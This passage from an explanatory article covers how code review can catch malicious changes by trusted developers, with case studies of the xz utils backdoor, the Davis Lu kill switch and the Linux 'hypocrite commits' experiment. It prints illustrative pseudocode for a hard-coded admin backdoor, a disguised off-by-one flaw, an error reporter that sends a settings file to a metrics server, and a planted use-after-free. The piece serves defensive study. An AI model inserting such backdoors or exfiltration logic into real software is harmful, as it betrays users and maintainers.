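# Automated review of code changes for malicious insertions by trusted developers

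## What is a malicious change by a trusted developer, and what does a reviewer see?

Automated code review uses software to examine edits to a program before they take effect. Teams mostly use it to find bugs and enforce house style, but they can also use it to catch edits intended to do harm. A malicious change might open a hidden way into a system, weaken a security check or send private data to an outsider. Some of the tools that might find it examine code without running it (static analysis), while others run the code and watch what happens. Newer tools use large language models to read an edit much as a colleague would.

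A trusted developer is a person or account with a legitimate right to change or approve the code. Trusted developers are the hardest authors to guard against because passwords and access rules, which keep strangers out, do little to stop an employee or long-standing volunteer who turns against the project. Defense then depends largely on the person or tool that reviews the change.

### From edit to running software

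A developer first edits files on their own machine, where nobody else sees the work. When the work is ready, the developer records it as a commit, which is a set of edits stored with an author's name, a date and a short message about its purpose. The name, date and message normally come from the developer's own machine, so a reviewer first learns about a change from its author's account of it.

The developer then opens a pull request to merge one or more commits into the shared code. The reviewer sees a diff, the line-by-line difference between the old code and the new, usually with a few unchanged lines around each edit. The diff mostly leaves out the functions that the new lines call, the settings they depend on and the outside libraries they use. Some files have no readable diff. SLSA's *Threats & mitigations*, a catalogue of attacks in an industry specification for software supply chains,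 gives the example of an altered JPEG image, for which the reviewer may get only a comparison of raw binary data. The catalogue also notes that a pull request normally shows the net effect of all its commits. If one commit adds something harmful and a later one removes it, the diff looks clean, but the harmful version stays in the project's history, and developers can still load it onto their machines. Its remedy is to put every commit through the full process, or to let each review produce only one commit.

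Continuous integration (CI) runs automated builds and tests on each change and shows the reviewer a pass or a fail. A pass means that the program behaved as expected on the inputs that were tested. Code that is triggered only by other inputs also passes, and the developer who made the change has often written its tests.

After a developer submits a change, a colleague reads the diff and asks questions before approving it. Many organisations require two-party approval, a rule that no change takes effect until someone other than its author has approved it. SLSA describes several ways around this rule that need no clever code. A team may exempt documentation files from review, or let an automated account submit changes without approval. One person may control two accounts, or an administrator may temporarily switch off the rule. A reviewer may also approve a change without reading it, which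 developers call rubber-stamping.

The merge follows approval and makes the change part of the main code. If the author can still edit the pull request after a colleague has approved it, the merged code may differ from the code the colleague read. A platform can prevent this by cancelling approvals whenever the pull request changes, but this requires a good deal of repeated reviewing.

The last steps are the build, which turns source code into a program that runs, and the release, which delivers it to users. Someone reviewing a pull request ordinarily sees neither. The current SLSA specification cites two well-known cases. At SolarWinds, attackers compromised the build platform and installed an implant that injected malicious behaviour during each build. At Codecov, an attacker used leaked credentials to upload a malicious file to the location where users downloaded the product. Reviewers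 would have missed both attacks even if they had read every diff perfectly. Open-source projects have a further gap, because distributors often build from a release archive, a package of source code that can differ from the repository that reviewers saw.

### Whose name is on the change

How a reviewer judges a diff depends partly on who wrote it. An outsider can only propose a change, which someone with merge rights must then merge. Reviewers have no history with the outsider and have good reason to ask why the change is needed.

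Stealing a developer's account gives an attacker an advantage, because colleagues may question a change less when it comes from a trusted senior employee, as BoostSecurity's *SLSA dip at the source of the problem* points out. But the attacker has to act like the account's owner to avoid suspicion. *S3C2 Summit 2025-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2026) describes a meeting where ten practitioners from eight companies discussed telltale signs, such as commits at unusual times, unexpected patterns of file edits, and sudden changes to the cryptographic keys that identify a developer. The real owner may also notice a commit they never made.

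All of these signs can disappear when the developer has earned the team's trust. The commits arrive at the usual hours, with the right keys, in files this person has edited for years, and the developer won't report them as someone else's work. The developer knows what the tests cover and which colleagues read carefully, and can include the malicious lines in work the team wanted anyway. An outsider can also work towards this position. *S3C2 Summit 2024-08* (Miller, Enck and colleagues, 2025) describes how the person behind the 2024 backdoor in the compression tool xz utils first slowly became an innocuous-looking maintainer. The remaining evidence is mostly in what the new lines do and whether that fits the reason given for adding them.

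### Four kinds of insertion

The simplest malicious change is an open payload, which does its damage whenever the code runs.

```
function nightly_cleanup():
    delete(temporary_files)
    delete(customer_records)
```

Anyone who reads the last line and knows what the function is for will object to it. An open payload therefore works best when nobody reviews the change. In a case that SLSA cites, a contractor with access to the code of SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency exchange, pushed a commit that redirected funds to the contractor. A second person reviewing the commit could have caught it.

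A backdoor stays quiet until something sets it off. It is hidden functionality that gives extra access or privileges to whoever knows its trigger.

```
function log_in(name, password):
    if name == "special-guest":
        return administrator_session
    return check_password(name, password)
```

Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors* (2018), break every backdoor into four components: an input source (here the login form), a trigger (the comparison with "special-guest"), a payload (the step that skips the password check) and a privileged state (the administrator's session). The backdoor doesn't work if any of them is missing. The trigger is the most useful component for a reviewer, because an explicit trigger has to appear in the code as a condition, and a reviewer can question a condition that looks odd. It also makes the backdoor hard to find by testing, since ordinary tests are unlikely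 to include the name "special-guest". A kill switch has a similar structure, but its payload disables a system and its trigger is often an event, such as the closing of an account.

A deliberate vulnerability is an exploitable flaw that a developer adds on purpose and disguises as an ordinary mistake. It contains no secret name or visible payload.

```
function get_page(document, n):
    # pages are numbered from 0
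    if n >= 0 and n <= document.page_count:
        return document.pages[n]
```

The second comparison should be "less than". A document of ten pages has pages 0 to 9, but this check also accepts a request for page 10, which does not exist. In many languages the program would stop with an error, but C does not check such limits, so the program may read whatever is next in memory, which could be somebody's password. Whether an attacker can use the flaw depends on code elsewhere.

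Exfiltration logic sends secrets, data or the trained numbers of an AI model to a place they should not go.

```
function report_error(error):
    report = error.message + contents(settings_file)
    send(report, METRICS_SERVER)
```

Programs routinely report errors, and attaching the settings helps whoever fixes the fault. The harm depends on whether the settings file holds passwords and who controls the metrics server, and the diff may not show either. A reviewer has to trace the data from its source to its destination, possibly through several files. A developer can also combine kinds of malicious change, for example by putting exfiltration logic behind a trigger or guarding a deliberate vulnerability with a check for a particular user.

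### Why a deliberate vulnerability is deniable

If a reviewer does spot the faulty comparison in `get_page`, its author can say "good catch" and fix it, just as an honest colleague would. Programmers often make this mistake, which is called an off-by-one error.

Thomas and Francillon compare the system the developer meant to build, the system that exists, and the system its users expect. An intentional backdoor is in the developer's plan and in the real program, but users do not expect it. An accidental vulnerability is only in the real program. An analyst needs the developer's plan to tell them apart, but has only the program. Where the code explicitly contains the step from trigger to payload, as in `log_in`, Thomas and Francillon treat the developer's intent as proven. Where that step depends on a bug, they call the construct a deniable backdoor if there are non-technical grounds for suspicion.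 They concede that nobody can distinguish a deniable backdoor from an accident on technical evidence alone.

They also analysed eleven real backdoors, including one in D-Link routers that let in anyone whose browser identified itself with a particular string. All eleven were explicit and so, by this definition, not deniable. This is weak evidence that attackers prefer explicit backdoors, because a deniable one that worked as intended would probably have been recorded as a bug.

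To judge intent, a reviewer can also check the version history for when a flaw was introduced and by which account, and ask whether the change had any legitimate reason. Thomas and Francillon regard such arguments as human intuition rather than proof, and the practitioners whom Rahman and colleagues recorded likewise found intent very hard to determine from a single commit. Before a merge, though, the reviewer doesn't need to know the intent, because the comparison needs fixing either way. A check that finds vulnerabilities in general will find some deliberate ones. Deniability lowers the risk to a malicious author, who may lose their job if caught with a hard-coded administrator login but can try again if caught with an off-by-one error.

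### The Davis Lu case

Davis Lu could hardly have passed off his kill switch as a mistake. Lu had worked since November 2007 as a software developer for a company in Beachwood, Ohio. Greig's *Chinese national who sabotaged Ohio company's systems handed four-year jail stint* (2025) cites a Cleveland.com report that identifies the employer as Eaton, a power management company. According to the U.S. Department of Justice's *Chinese National Who Deployed "Kill Switch" Code on Employer's Network Sentenced* (2025), the sabotage began after a 2018 reorganisation cut Lu's responsibilities and system access. By 4 August 2019 he had introduced code that kept creating new threads (parallel strands of work inside a program) without ending them, until servers crashed or hung. He also deleted colleagues' profile files. The kill switch checked whether his own account was still enabled in Active Directory,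 the company's register of users, and locked everyone out if it was not. He named it "IsDLEnabledinAD", short for "Is Davis Lu enabled in Active Directory".

It activated on 9 September 2019 and affected thousands of users around the world. According to the Department of Justice release, Lu was placed on leave that day, but the Cleveland prosecutors' announcement, *Chinese National Sentenced to Prison for Deploying Destructive Computer Code*, says he was terminated. Both date the end of his employment to October, which fits leave better than termination. A jury convicted him in March 2025 of causing intentional damage to protected computers, and his lawyer said that month that he planned to appeal. In August a judge sentenced him to four years in prison.

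The case is of limited use as a test of code review. According to *Software developer charged with damaging the computer system of a Cleveland company*, the announcement of the indictment, the company found the thread-creating code while investigating a crash of its production servers. Bitdefender adds that the malicious program was on a development server that only Lu could access, and that someone had used his account to run it on the production systems. These accounts don't mention a colleague reading the code first. A reader might have taken "DL" for "distribution list", a common abbreviation in that setting, but a function that locks out every user is hard to explain away. The case more clearly shows a weakness in access control, since one person could put code into production without anyone else's approval.

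### Measuring a check

A check meant to catch such code earlier can fail by missing a malicious change or by flagging a harmless one. Three figures describe its performance. The detection rate is the share of malicious changes it flags, the false-alarm rate is the share of harmless changes it flags, and precision is the share of flagged changes that are malicious.

Suppose a company merges 10,010 changes in a year, of which 10 are malicious (a dreadful year), and a check flags 8 of the 10 along with 200 of the 10,000 harmless ones. Its detection rate is 80% and its false-alarm rate 2%. Its precision is 8 out of 208, or about 4%, so the security team investigates 26 alarms for every real attack. In general, for *M* malicious and *H* harmless changes,

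precision = (detection rate × *M*) / (detection rate × *M* + false-alarm rate × *H*).

When malicious changes are rare, *H* is so much larger than *M* that precision depends mostly on the false-alarm rate. Cutting that rate from 2% to 0.1% would leave 10 false alarms and raise precision to 44%, with the same detection rate.

The formula also explains why a tool can have higher precision in a test than in daily use. If the original check is run on 100 malicious and 100 harmless changes, it flags 80 of the malicious ones and 2 of the harmless ones, for a precision of 98%. The same check had a precision of 4% at the company. Detection and false-alarm rates carry over from a test to daily use if the test changes resemble the real ones, but precision carries over only if malicious changes are also about as common in both. The real detection rate will be lower than the measured one if a trusted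 developer can try the tool on a draft first.

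## How did the xz utils backdoor get past review?

XZ Utils is a set of free compression tools, and many basic parts of a Linux system use its library, liblzma. In February and March 2024 a co-maintainer known as Jia Tan published two versions, 5.6.0 and 5.6.1, with a backdoor that let its owner run commands on a server without logging in. The project developed its code in public, so researchers could later review Jia Tan's work commit by commit and see what information each check would have had.

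### From first patch to discovery

Lasse Collin had maintained XZ Utils since 2009, unpaid and largely alone. According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Cox, 2024), Jia Tan, presumably a pseudonym, sent the project's mailing list a harmless file of editor settings on 29 October 2021. More patches followed, and they look fine even in retrospect. In November 2021, another open-source project, libarchive, merged a change from the same account that replaced a safe printing function with a less safe one. Lins and colleagues (2024), in *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, call this the first suspicious commit but say they could not tell whether it was related to xz.

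In spring 2022 two other users, calling themselves Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens, began to complain on the mailing list about slow progress and to press Collin to hand over the project. Collin answered that the project was an unpaid hobby and that Jia Tan might take a bigger role. Their email addresses never appeared anywhere else, even in data breaches, and Cox thinks Kumar and Ens were probably fakes. By 30 December 2022 Jia Tan could merge changes directly. Cox dates Jia Tan's first release to March 2023, while Przymus and Durieux (2025), in *Wolves in the Repository*, put it in December 2022. They also found that most of Jia Tan's contributions were to documentation and translations, which build a record of useful work and attract little scrutiny.

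In June 2023 a contributor called Hans Jansen offered patches that used ifunc, a feature that lets a library choose between versions of a function when a program starts. Collin reworked them and Jia Tan merged them. The backdoor later depended on this feature, though nobody has established whether the patches were part of the plan.

On 23 February 2024 Jia Tan added the files that contained the backdoor and released version 5.6.0 the next day. Debian, a large Linux distribution, added that release to its development version on 26 February, and Fedora shipped it in test versions. Version 5.6.1 followed on 9 March. On 25 March Hans Jansen reappeared and asked Debian to adopt the new version, and Debian did so two days later.

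Andres Freund, a database developer at Microsoft, meanwhile noticed that logins over SSH, the standard way to reach a server remotely, were using a lot of processor time on his Debian machines. A login attempt that should have failed in 0.3 seconds took 0.8. He traced the delay to liblzma and at first suspected Debian's own package. He alerted Debian on 28 March, and it withdrew the release the same day. On 29 March he published his findings in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024). Few distributions had adopted the bad versions by then, and those that had did so mostly in pre-releases. Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor.

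### How the backdoor worked

Jia Tan hid the payload, a piece of compiled code, in binary files that passed as test data. A compression library needs such files, including deliberately damaged ones, to check that it handles them properly. The payload did nothing until an altered build file, part of the scripts that prepare a program for compiling, unpacked it and linked it into liblzma. This build file was only in the release archives and never in the Git repository, according to the Tukaani Project's *xz backdoor*, Collin's statement on the incident.

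The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, a widely used SSH program that does not itself need liblzma. Debian and several other distributions modify OpenSSH to notify systemd, which starts and stops a machine's services, that it is running. The systemd library they use for this loads liblzma, so the payload could run inside the OpenSSH server. The payload used ifunc to start early, while the server's table of function addresses was still writable, and replaced the address of a function that checks signatures at login.

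Logins that used that function then went through the attacker's code. If a client presented a certificate made with the attacker's private key, the code ran a command hidden in the certificate, and the command had full control of the machine. Otherwise, the code apparently passed the login to the normal check. In Thomas and Francillon's terms, the certificate was the input source and the match with the attacker's key was the trigger.

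No single place held all of this at once:

| Where a check could look | Payload in test files | Altered build file | Working backdoor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Git repository, from 23 February | yes | no | no |
| Archive generated by GitHub, from 24 February | yes | no | no |
| Archive made by Jia Tan, from 24 February | yes | yes | no |
| Compiled library in Debian, from 26 February | no | no | yes |

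### Reading the diff

Someone who read every commit as it arrived would have seen almost entirely ordinary work. Przymus and Durieux count eight malicious commits in a dataset of 1,020. Collin knew the project's code very well and read a good deal of what Jia Tan wrote. In his commit-by-commit review for the Tukaani Project, written after the attack, he recalls fixing a memory leak a few days after one commit, reverting another he disliked, and accepting some additions because Jia Tan kept insisting.

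A reader checking the payload could see only file names and that binary files had been added. The project's README had long included a note that many test files were made by hand, byte by byte, and had no better source than the files themselves. Jia Tan replaced two of the files on 9 March and wrote in the commit message that the originals came from random data and that the new ones used a fixed seed, to make them easier to reproduce. A sceptical reader could have asked for the program that generated them. Lins and colleagues recommend storing the commands that create test files instead of the finished files.

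The automated tests did not catch the backdoor either. Collin points out that the test script tries to decompress every file in the folder, although Freund wrote that no test used the new files in 5.6.0. A file that decompresses correctly, or fails in the expected way, passes such a test whatever else it contains.

One malicious edit was in readable text. In late February Jia Tan changed the build system's check for Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program may do, and left a stray full stop at the start of a line. The check works by compiling a tiny test program. The full stop was a syntax error, so the program never compiled and the build always treated Landlock as missing. The commit lists Collin as the committer, and Cox thinks Collin probably missed the typo.

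The Landlock edit was separate from the SSH backdoor, and its author could have passed it off as a mistake. It was the malicious change that an automated check could most easily have caught, since the compiler rejected the test program every time and the build ignored the reason. Przymus and Durieux write that the developers of Autoconf, a common build tool, have since been adding syntax checks for such test programs.

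### Could code analysis have caught it?

A week after the disclosure, Jonathan Werrett, head of security at the static analysis company Semgrep, wrote in *Three key learnings for AppSec teams from the XZ backdoor* (2024) that no code analysis product had caught the backdoor or could have. His reasons were that key elements were outside the repository and that the attacker had plenty of time to get around any checks.

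Tools that read the C code in the repository would have missed the payload, because it was already compiled and wasn't in that code. The code did include ifunc, but ifunc has legitimate uses. Taint analysis, which follows data from a sensitive source to a dangerous destination, would have had no path to follow, because the build created the connection later.

The claim is too broad for build scripts. Werrett describes the archives as binary, but they were source archives, and the altered build file was text. He also says it was there for anyone to see. Cox (2024), in *The xz attack shell script*, finds the alterations fairly plausible at a glance, since they updated the version number and copyright year and added inscrutable lines to a file that was already hard to read. The added lines did something much stranger than their appearance suggested, making the build decode data from a test file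 and run the result as commands. A static rule against running decoded data during a build could have flagged this on 24 February, if someone had applied it to the archive. The false-alarm rate of such a rule is unknown, and an attacker who knew about the rule would have looked for another way to write the same step.

Werrett is nearly right about binary files. A tool could flag every new binary file that comes without a program to generate it. This would have caught the 23 February commit, but it would also flag legitimate test files made by hand. Telling which files contain hidden code is far harder in a compression project, where well-compressed data looks random and some files are damaged on purpose. Antivirus programs did flag the two files after the disclosure, but by then antivirus makers knew what to look for.

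After the backdoor was discovered, Semgrep's engineers also wrote a rule that looks for RC4, an outdated encryption method. Werrett calls the rule experimental and too slow to switch on by default. It is named after the malicious script, which was compressed and scrambled inside a test file, so Semgrep would first have needed an unpacked copy.

Comparing the archive with the repository is a simpler form of code analysis that would not have required anyone to understand the payload.

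### The gap between repository and release archive

From the day of its release, Jia Tan's archive contained the altered build file, which was not in the repository. GitHub also generated an archive of the same version without the file and offered it on the same page. An automatic comparison of the two archives could have detected the file before any distribution adopted 5.6.0.

Comparing the release archive with the repository would have flagged many harmless files. Developers of C projects commonly run Autoconf on their own machines and add the generated scripts to the archive, which makes the program easier for distributions to build. Legitimate xz archives had always contained such scripts. A maintainer who receives a long list of expected differences at every release will soon stop reading it.

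A better method is to compare each added file with its public original. Jia Tan had altered a file from Gnulib, a shared collection of code. Funk (2024) compared the two versions and published the differences in a reply to Freund's post, less than 15 hours after it was sent. Anyone could have done the same on 24 February. Routine checks of this kind would need an up-to-date collection of originals, and they would flag projects that had changed a shared file for honest reasons. Jia Tan's copy also had a higher version number than the original, so a tool that skipped unrecognised versions would have missed it.

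Many other projects have the same gap. Lins and colleagues looked at roughly 61 Debian packages that popular internet-facing server software depends on. Only 10 used the archive generated automatically from the repository. The researchers could not identify the exact origin of the code for 9, and the rest used separately made archives or a different distribution channel.

Distributions can avoid the gap by building directly from the repository. Arch Linux switched xz to this method on 28 March, and the operating system Haiku followed two days later. Lins and colleagues also suggest having CI produce the archives, so that their contents are determined by code anyone can inspect. Either method would have forced Jia Tan to put the build instructions where reviewers could see them in a diff, although reviewers might still not have objected.

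### Rebuilding from source

In a reproducible build, independent builders who start from the same source get identical files, and any difference points to tampering during the build. This check would have missed the xz backdoor if everyone had started from Jia Tan's archive, because each builder would have produced the same compromised library. A signature check would also have missed it, because Jia Tan was authorized to sign releases and had signed the backdoored ones.

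A build from the repository would have produced a clean library, so comparing it with Debian's could have exposed the extra code. But differences between builds are hard to interpret, because Autoconf adapts a program to the machine it is built on, so builds without malicious code can also differ.

An investigator could also have built the software from the bad archive and got a clean result. The malicious script added the payload only on certain systems, and only during the build of a Debian package or an RPM package (the format used by Fedora and Red Hat). Freund thinks the packaging condition was probably meant to make the problem harder to reproduce.

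### Fuzzing

The project had one strong automated test, and Jia Tan weakened it. OSS-Fuzz, a free service from Google, runs open-source programs on huge numbers of generated inputs to find crashes and memory errors. In March 2023, with Collin's approval, Jia Tan became OSS-Fuzz's main contact for xz and began receiving its bug reports. On 7 July, Jia Tan asked OSS-Fuzz to build xz without ifunc, saying that ifunc was incompatible with a tool for detecting memory errors.

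Lins and colleagues confirm that there was a compatibility problem. A bot labelled the request as ready to merge because Jia Tan was a listed contact with a history of contributions, and OSS-Fuzz soon accepted it. A Google engineer later explained that developers decide for themselves which parts of their project OSS-Fuzz tests.

Leaving ifunc on probably would not have exposed the backdoor. Builds from the repository lacked the altered build file, and the payload was added only when building a Debian or RPM package. Even on a compromised login server, a fuzzer would have had practically no chance of producing the required certificate without the attacker's private key.

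*Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026), which presents a fuzzing tool for finding backdoors but does not test it on xz, offers another explanation for the request. Fuzzing services report which code they fail to reach, and the attackers may not have wanted to draw attention to theirs. They may also have wanted to hide ordinary ifunc bugs. On the day of the release, crashes began to appear on the Gentoo distribution, and they seem to have come from such a bug, not from the backdoor.

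### Errors and slow logins

Tests of the finished software did find errors more than three weeks before Freund's discovery. On 4 March, Valgrind, a tool that monitors how a running program uses memory, began reporting errors in Red Hat's distributions. They came from the function where the backdoor started running, because the payload relied on a memory layout that was wrong in some configurations.

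Jia Tan was the person best placed to explain the errors. On 8 March Jia Tan committed a supposed fix, which Cox calls a misdirection, and the next day made the real repair by replacing the test files. Freund notes that the same account had discussed the "fixes" on various mailing lists. An automated check is much weaker when its warnings go to the developer who caused them and that developer can declare them resolved.

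Performance measurements could also have caught the backdoor before Freund did, but only if they covered OpenSSH, which had become slower on distributions that had modified it to work with systemd. The xz project's own benchmarks would naturally time compression, which had not slowed. A distribution that timed SSH logins before and after every package update could have seen the delay from 26 February onward.

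The login server had to start in the normal way for the delay to appear, because the payload checked its environment and looked for some debugging tools. When Freund first started the server by hand, the delay disappeared. The payload spent most of the extra time searching tables of function names in memory, so a more efficient one would have caused a shorter delay. A half-second delay is also easy to dismiss as the result of a bad update, and the discovery depended on Freund's willingness to find the cause.

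### Language models on the xz code

No published test seems to have had a language model review the xz commits or the release archive. In the closest study, *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models*, Udeshi, Putrevu and colleagues (2025) tested models on the compiled library. They compared version 5.6.0 with the clean version 5.4.7, using a decompiler to turn the machine code back into rough source code. A model then summarised the 79 functions that differed and scored how sensitive each one's behaviour was. Finally, a model had to decide from the five highest-scoring functions whether the update was malicious.

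GPT-5 correctly judged the update malicious, whether it used its own summaries or those written by the smaller GPT-5 mini. GPT-5 mini judged the update malicious when it used GPT-5's summaries but benign when it used its own. Both models ranked the injected functions in their top five, so GPT-5 mini had flagged the right code but failed to conclude from its own summaries that the update was malicious.

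The result is encouraging but is weak evidence of what would have happened in February 2024. The backdoor had been public for about 18 months by the time of the test, so the models may have been trained on descriptions of it. Udeshi and colleagues report no test on a harmless xz update, so the false-alarm rate on this library is unknown. Their method also needs a compiled library that already contains the backdoor, so it could have protected a distribution's users but not stopped the commit. Quesma's *We hid backdoors in ~40MB binaries* describes a harder test, in which AI agents searched compiled programs for backdoors. Claude Opus 4.6, the best model at the time, found relatively obvious ones in 49% of attempts, and most models often flagged clean programs.

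A model reviewing the xz commits would have faced the same opaque test files as Collin, though it might have noticed the stray full stop in the Landlock check. Given the release archive and Gnulib's original build file, it could also have been asked to explain the changes to that file, which is much easier than finding a backdoor in machine code.

### What one discovered case says about the others

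The xz case proves that a patient developer can get a backdoor into widely used software, but it cannot be used to estimate how often this happens. If there are *N* such backdoors and each has a probability *p* of being found, the expected number of discoveries is *N* × *p*. This equals one for a single backdoor that is certain to be found, but also for 20 backdoors with a 5% chance each, of which an average of 19 would remain undiscovered.

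Przymus and Durieux call the discovery lucky, which suggests that *p* is low. But the luck may have been mostly in the timing. Valgrind had already reported errors, and many more people would have run the library once it reached stable distributions. The systemd developers had also merged a change on 5 March, apparently for unrelated reasons, that stopped their library from loading liblzma. According to Cox, this would have defeated the attack. We can't tell how long the backdoor would have survived if Freund hadn't found it.

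Lins and colleagues argue that the security community has to assume that similarly sophisticated attacks are active in other projects, including closed-source ones. This is a reasonable assumption for planning defences, but they have no count of such attacks to support it. The known case may also be unlike others, because Freund found it through a slow payload that caused memory errors, and a faster, less buggy backdoor might have gone unnoticed. Comparing build files with their originals would have exposed Jia Tan's archive on the first day, but it would not catch a developer who put a deliberate vulnerability in the ordinary source code.

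## What did the Linux "hypocrite commits" experiment show?

In August 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota tested whether reviewers would notice that kind of flaw. They emailed the maintainers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, small fixes that also introduced a more serious bug, which they did not disclose. Their paper, *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, calls such a change a "hypocrite commit".

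Anyone can propose a change to the kernel by emailing a patch, which is a diff with an explanation. The maintainers of the affected code read it, sometimes using simple analysis tools, and apply it if they are satisfied. Wu and Lu assumed an attacker with no standing in the project, who could submit only minor fixes of fewer than 30 lines.

### One edit short of a vulnerability

A vulnerability often needs several conditions, which may be in different parts of a program. Wu and Lu call code that meets only some of these conditions an "immature vulnerability". Such code is safe as it stands, but one more plausible edit could complete the flaw.

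The researchers worked with use-after-free flaws. A program written in C requests memory from the system and releases ("frees") it when finished. If the program keeps using that memory, it may be using a location that now holds something else. It may then crash or reveal data, and an attacker who controls the new contents may be able to take over the machine. The flaw occurs only if the program releases the memory, uses it, and does so in that order. In this simplified example, the plus sign marks the line that a patch adds.

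```
  function disconnect(device):
      result = send_goodbye(device)
      free(device)
      return result

  function unplug(device):
      result = disconnect(device)
      if result == FAILED:
+         log("could not disconnect", device.name)
          return FAILED
```

Before the patch, `disconnect` released the device's memory and nothing used that memory afterwards. The new line looks helpful because it reports the failed device to an administrator, but it reads the device's name from the memory already released. The call to `free` might be in another file, outside the diff. A correct patch would save the name before calling `disconnect`.

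One real flaw of this type stayed in the kernel for five years. The kernel counts how many parts of the program still need an object and releases the object when the count reaches zero. A developer noticed that one function did not lower this count after an error, and wrote a patch to lower it. The patch caused the object to be released, and another function then released it again. Wu and Lu treat the patch as an honest mistake.

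Immature vulnerabilities tend to stay in the code because they aren't bugs yet. Bug-finding tools don't report them, and the rules for the kernel's stable versions require a patch to fix a real bug. Adding precautions against them can also slow the kernel down.

### From thousands of candidates to three patches

Wu and Lu wrote two search programs with LLVM, a toolkit for building compilers. One looked for memory that a patch could plausibly release too early, and found 921 candidates. The other looked for released memory that a patch could plausibly use again, and found 4,657. Within a week, one researcher read 100 candidates of each type and picked three.

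They also counted 1,085 objects that different parts of the kernel might use and release at the same time. The three counts add up to 6,663, which is probably the source of their figure of more than 6,000 immature use-after-free vulnerabilities. These are possible starting points for an attack, and Wu and Lu do not estimate how many could lead to a working one. They concede that even the three they chose may not have been exploitable.

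Each of the three patches changed fewer than five lines and addressed a real but minor bug. The first added a missing error message, much like the example above. The second fixed a memory leak (memory that a program never releases) and the third fixed a faulty reference count, but both released the memory too early.

### What happened to the patches

Wu and Lu (2020) say in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* that they prepared a correct version of each patch in advance. Once a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they pointed out the bug, asked the maintainer not to apply the patch and supplied the correct version. By their account, maintainers confirmed in all three cases that they would not apply the flawed patch, and none became a commit in any branch of Linux.

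Kernel developers agree that no flawed patch got in, but they describe the review differently. *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*, by destinyland, quotes at length from an article in which the Linux news site LWN went through details the researchers disclosed in April 2021. The researchers had sent five patches from two false accounts. One was an ordinary fix sent from the wrong account by mistake. In another, they tried to plant a bug but got it wrong, so the patch was valid. The other three contained real bugs. Maintainers accepted none of them, though not always because of the planted bug.

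Cook's *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (2021) quotes a timeline that dates the five emails from 4 to 21 August 2020. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) puts the start of the experiment at 9 August, so the first email was presumably the ordinary fix. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, which includes several leading kernel developers, concluded that maintainers had "caught, or ignored" every invalid patch and that the review process had worked as intended, according to TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches*.

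These findings are hard to reconcile with the researchers' account, because if maintainers ignored one of the three flawed patches, nobody can have approved it and then agreed not to apply it. Derek Jones, in The Shape of Code's *Software engineering experiments* (2021), points out that Wu and Lu never report how many patches passed review. To protect the maintainers, Wu and Lu also simplified the published code and removed the names, so readers could not easily match the paper's three cases to emails. Some early coverage, such as PortSwigger's *University of Minnesota banned from Linux kernel contributions*, reported that the kernel had accepted the vulnerabilities, which the later findings contradict.

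In *Looking back at the UMN episode*, a comment on LWN, the reviewer error27 (2021) recalls catching other bugs in a patch, after which the researchers replied that the review had missed a use-after-free. According to error27, there was no use-after-free, because the calling function still held a reference to the object. The researchers disagreed.

### The ban and the second review

The experiment became a public scandal in April 2021, after another Minnesota researcher sent a faulty patch based on an experimental analysis tool. Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable versions, took it for another deliberately bad patch. *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers* (Edge, 2021) reported that he banned contributions from the university and prepared to undo 190 of its earlier commits. The new patch turned out to be an honest mistake. Objections to the experiment itself had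 begun in late 2020, when Linderud, Torres-Arias and colleagues asked the IEEE security symposium that had accepted the paper to reconsider. Critics said the study experimented on people without their consent and wasted their time. Wu and Lu answered that they were studying a process, not individuals. The university's ethics board agreed that this was not human research, but Wu and Lu had consulted it only after the experiment. They later apologised and withdrew the paper.

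The board also organised a second review of 435 kernel commits associated with the university. Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal* reports that developers found 349 correct and 39 in need of fixing, and that later commits had already fixed another 25. Of the remaining 22, one was removed at its author's request, and the others either no longer mattered or predated the research group. According to a commenter on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), the review took 85 developers.

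At least 64 of the 435 commits, or about 15%, were therefore faulty when maintainers merged them. A faulty commit is not necessarily a vulnerability, and we can't tell whether 15% is high without a figure for other contributors. Still, maintainers had earlier merged dozens of unintentional bugs under the same review process that stopped three planted ones.

### Why reviewers miss such flaws

Wu and Lu's better evidence is a set of 138 catalogued vulnerabilities from the kernel's history that minor patches had introduced by accident. Such patches accounted for 9.8% of the vulnerabilities they could trace. About 9% of the flaws were obvious enough to blame on carelessness. Reviewers had mostly missed the others because the danger depended on code outside the diff. Some flaws involved concurrency, where parts of the kernel run at the same time and their order can vary. Others were on error paths,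 which run only when something fails. Still others involved a function whose name doesn't show that it releases memory, or aliases, where a program reaches the same memory under two names.

To compare these features, Wu and Lu took use-after-free flaws from January 2015 to August 2020 and calculated a catch rate. This is the number of flaws that maintainers caught in review divided by the number caught plus the number merged.

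| Feature of the flaw | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| Baseline | 56.6% |
| Error path | 42.0% |
| Alias | 38.4% |
| Hidden release | 36.3% |
| Concurrency | 19.4% |

Wu and Lu call these rates upper bounds because some merged flaws are still undiscovered. But the number caught may also be too low, since a maintainer can reject a patch without mentioning the flaw, as happened in the experiment, so the true rates could be higher or lower. The order of the middle rows is also uncertain. Wu and Lu found that merged flaws on error paths survived longer than those with aliases or hidden releases, although reviewers had caught error-path flaws more often.

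Concurrency was the hardest feature on both measures, and later data support this. *A Deeper Look at 125,000 Kernel Vulnerabilities* (Qu, 2026) reports that kernel bugs stay hidden for 2.1 years on average, and that race conditions, which depend on the timing of concurrent code, go unnoticed more than twice as long as other types.

The catch rates are for bugs introduced by accident, so they can only suggest how often reviewers would catch an attacker's bugs. An attacker could choose the kinds of bug that are hardest to catch, which would push the catch rate towards the lowest in the table.

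### What the maintainers said and what the researchers proposed

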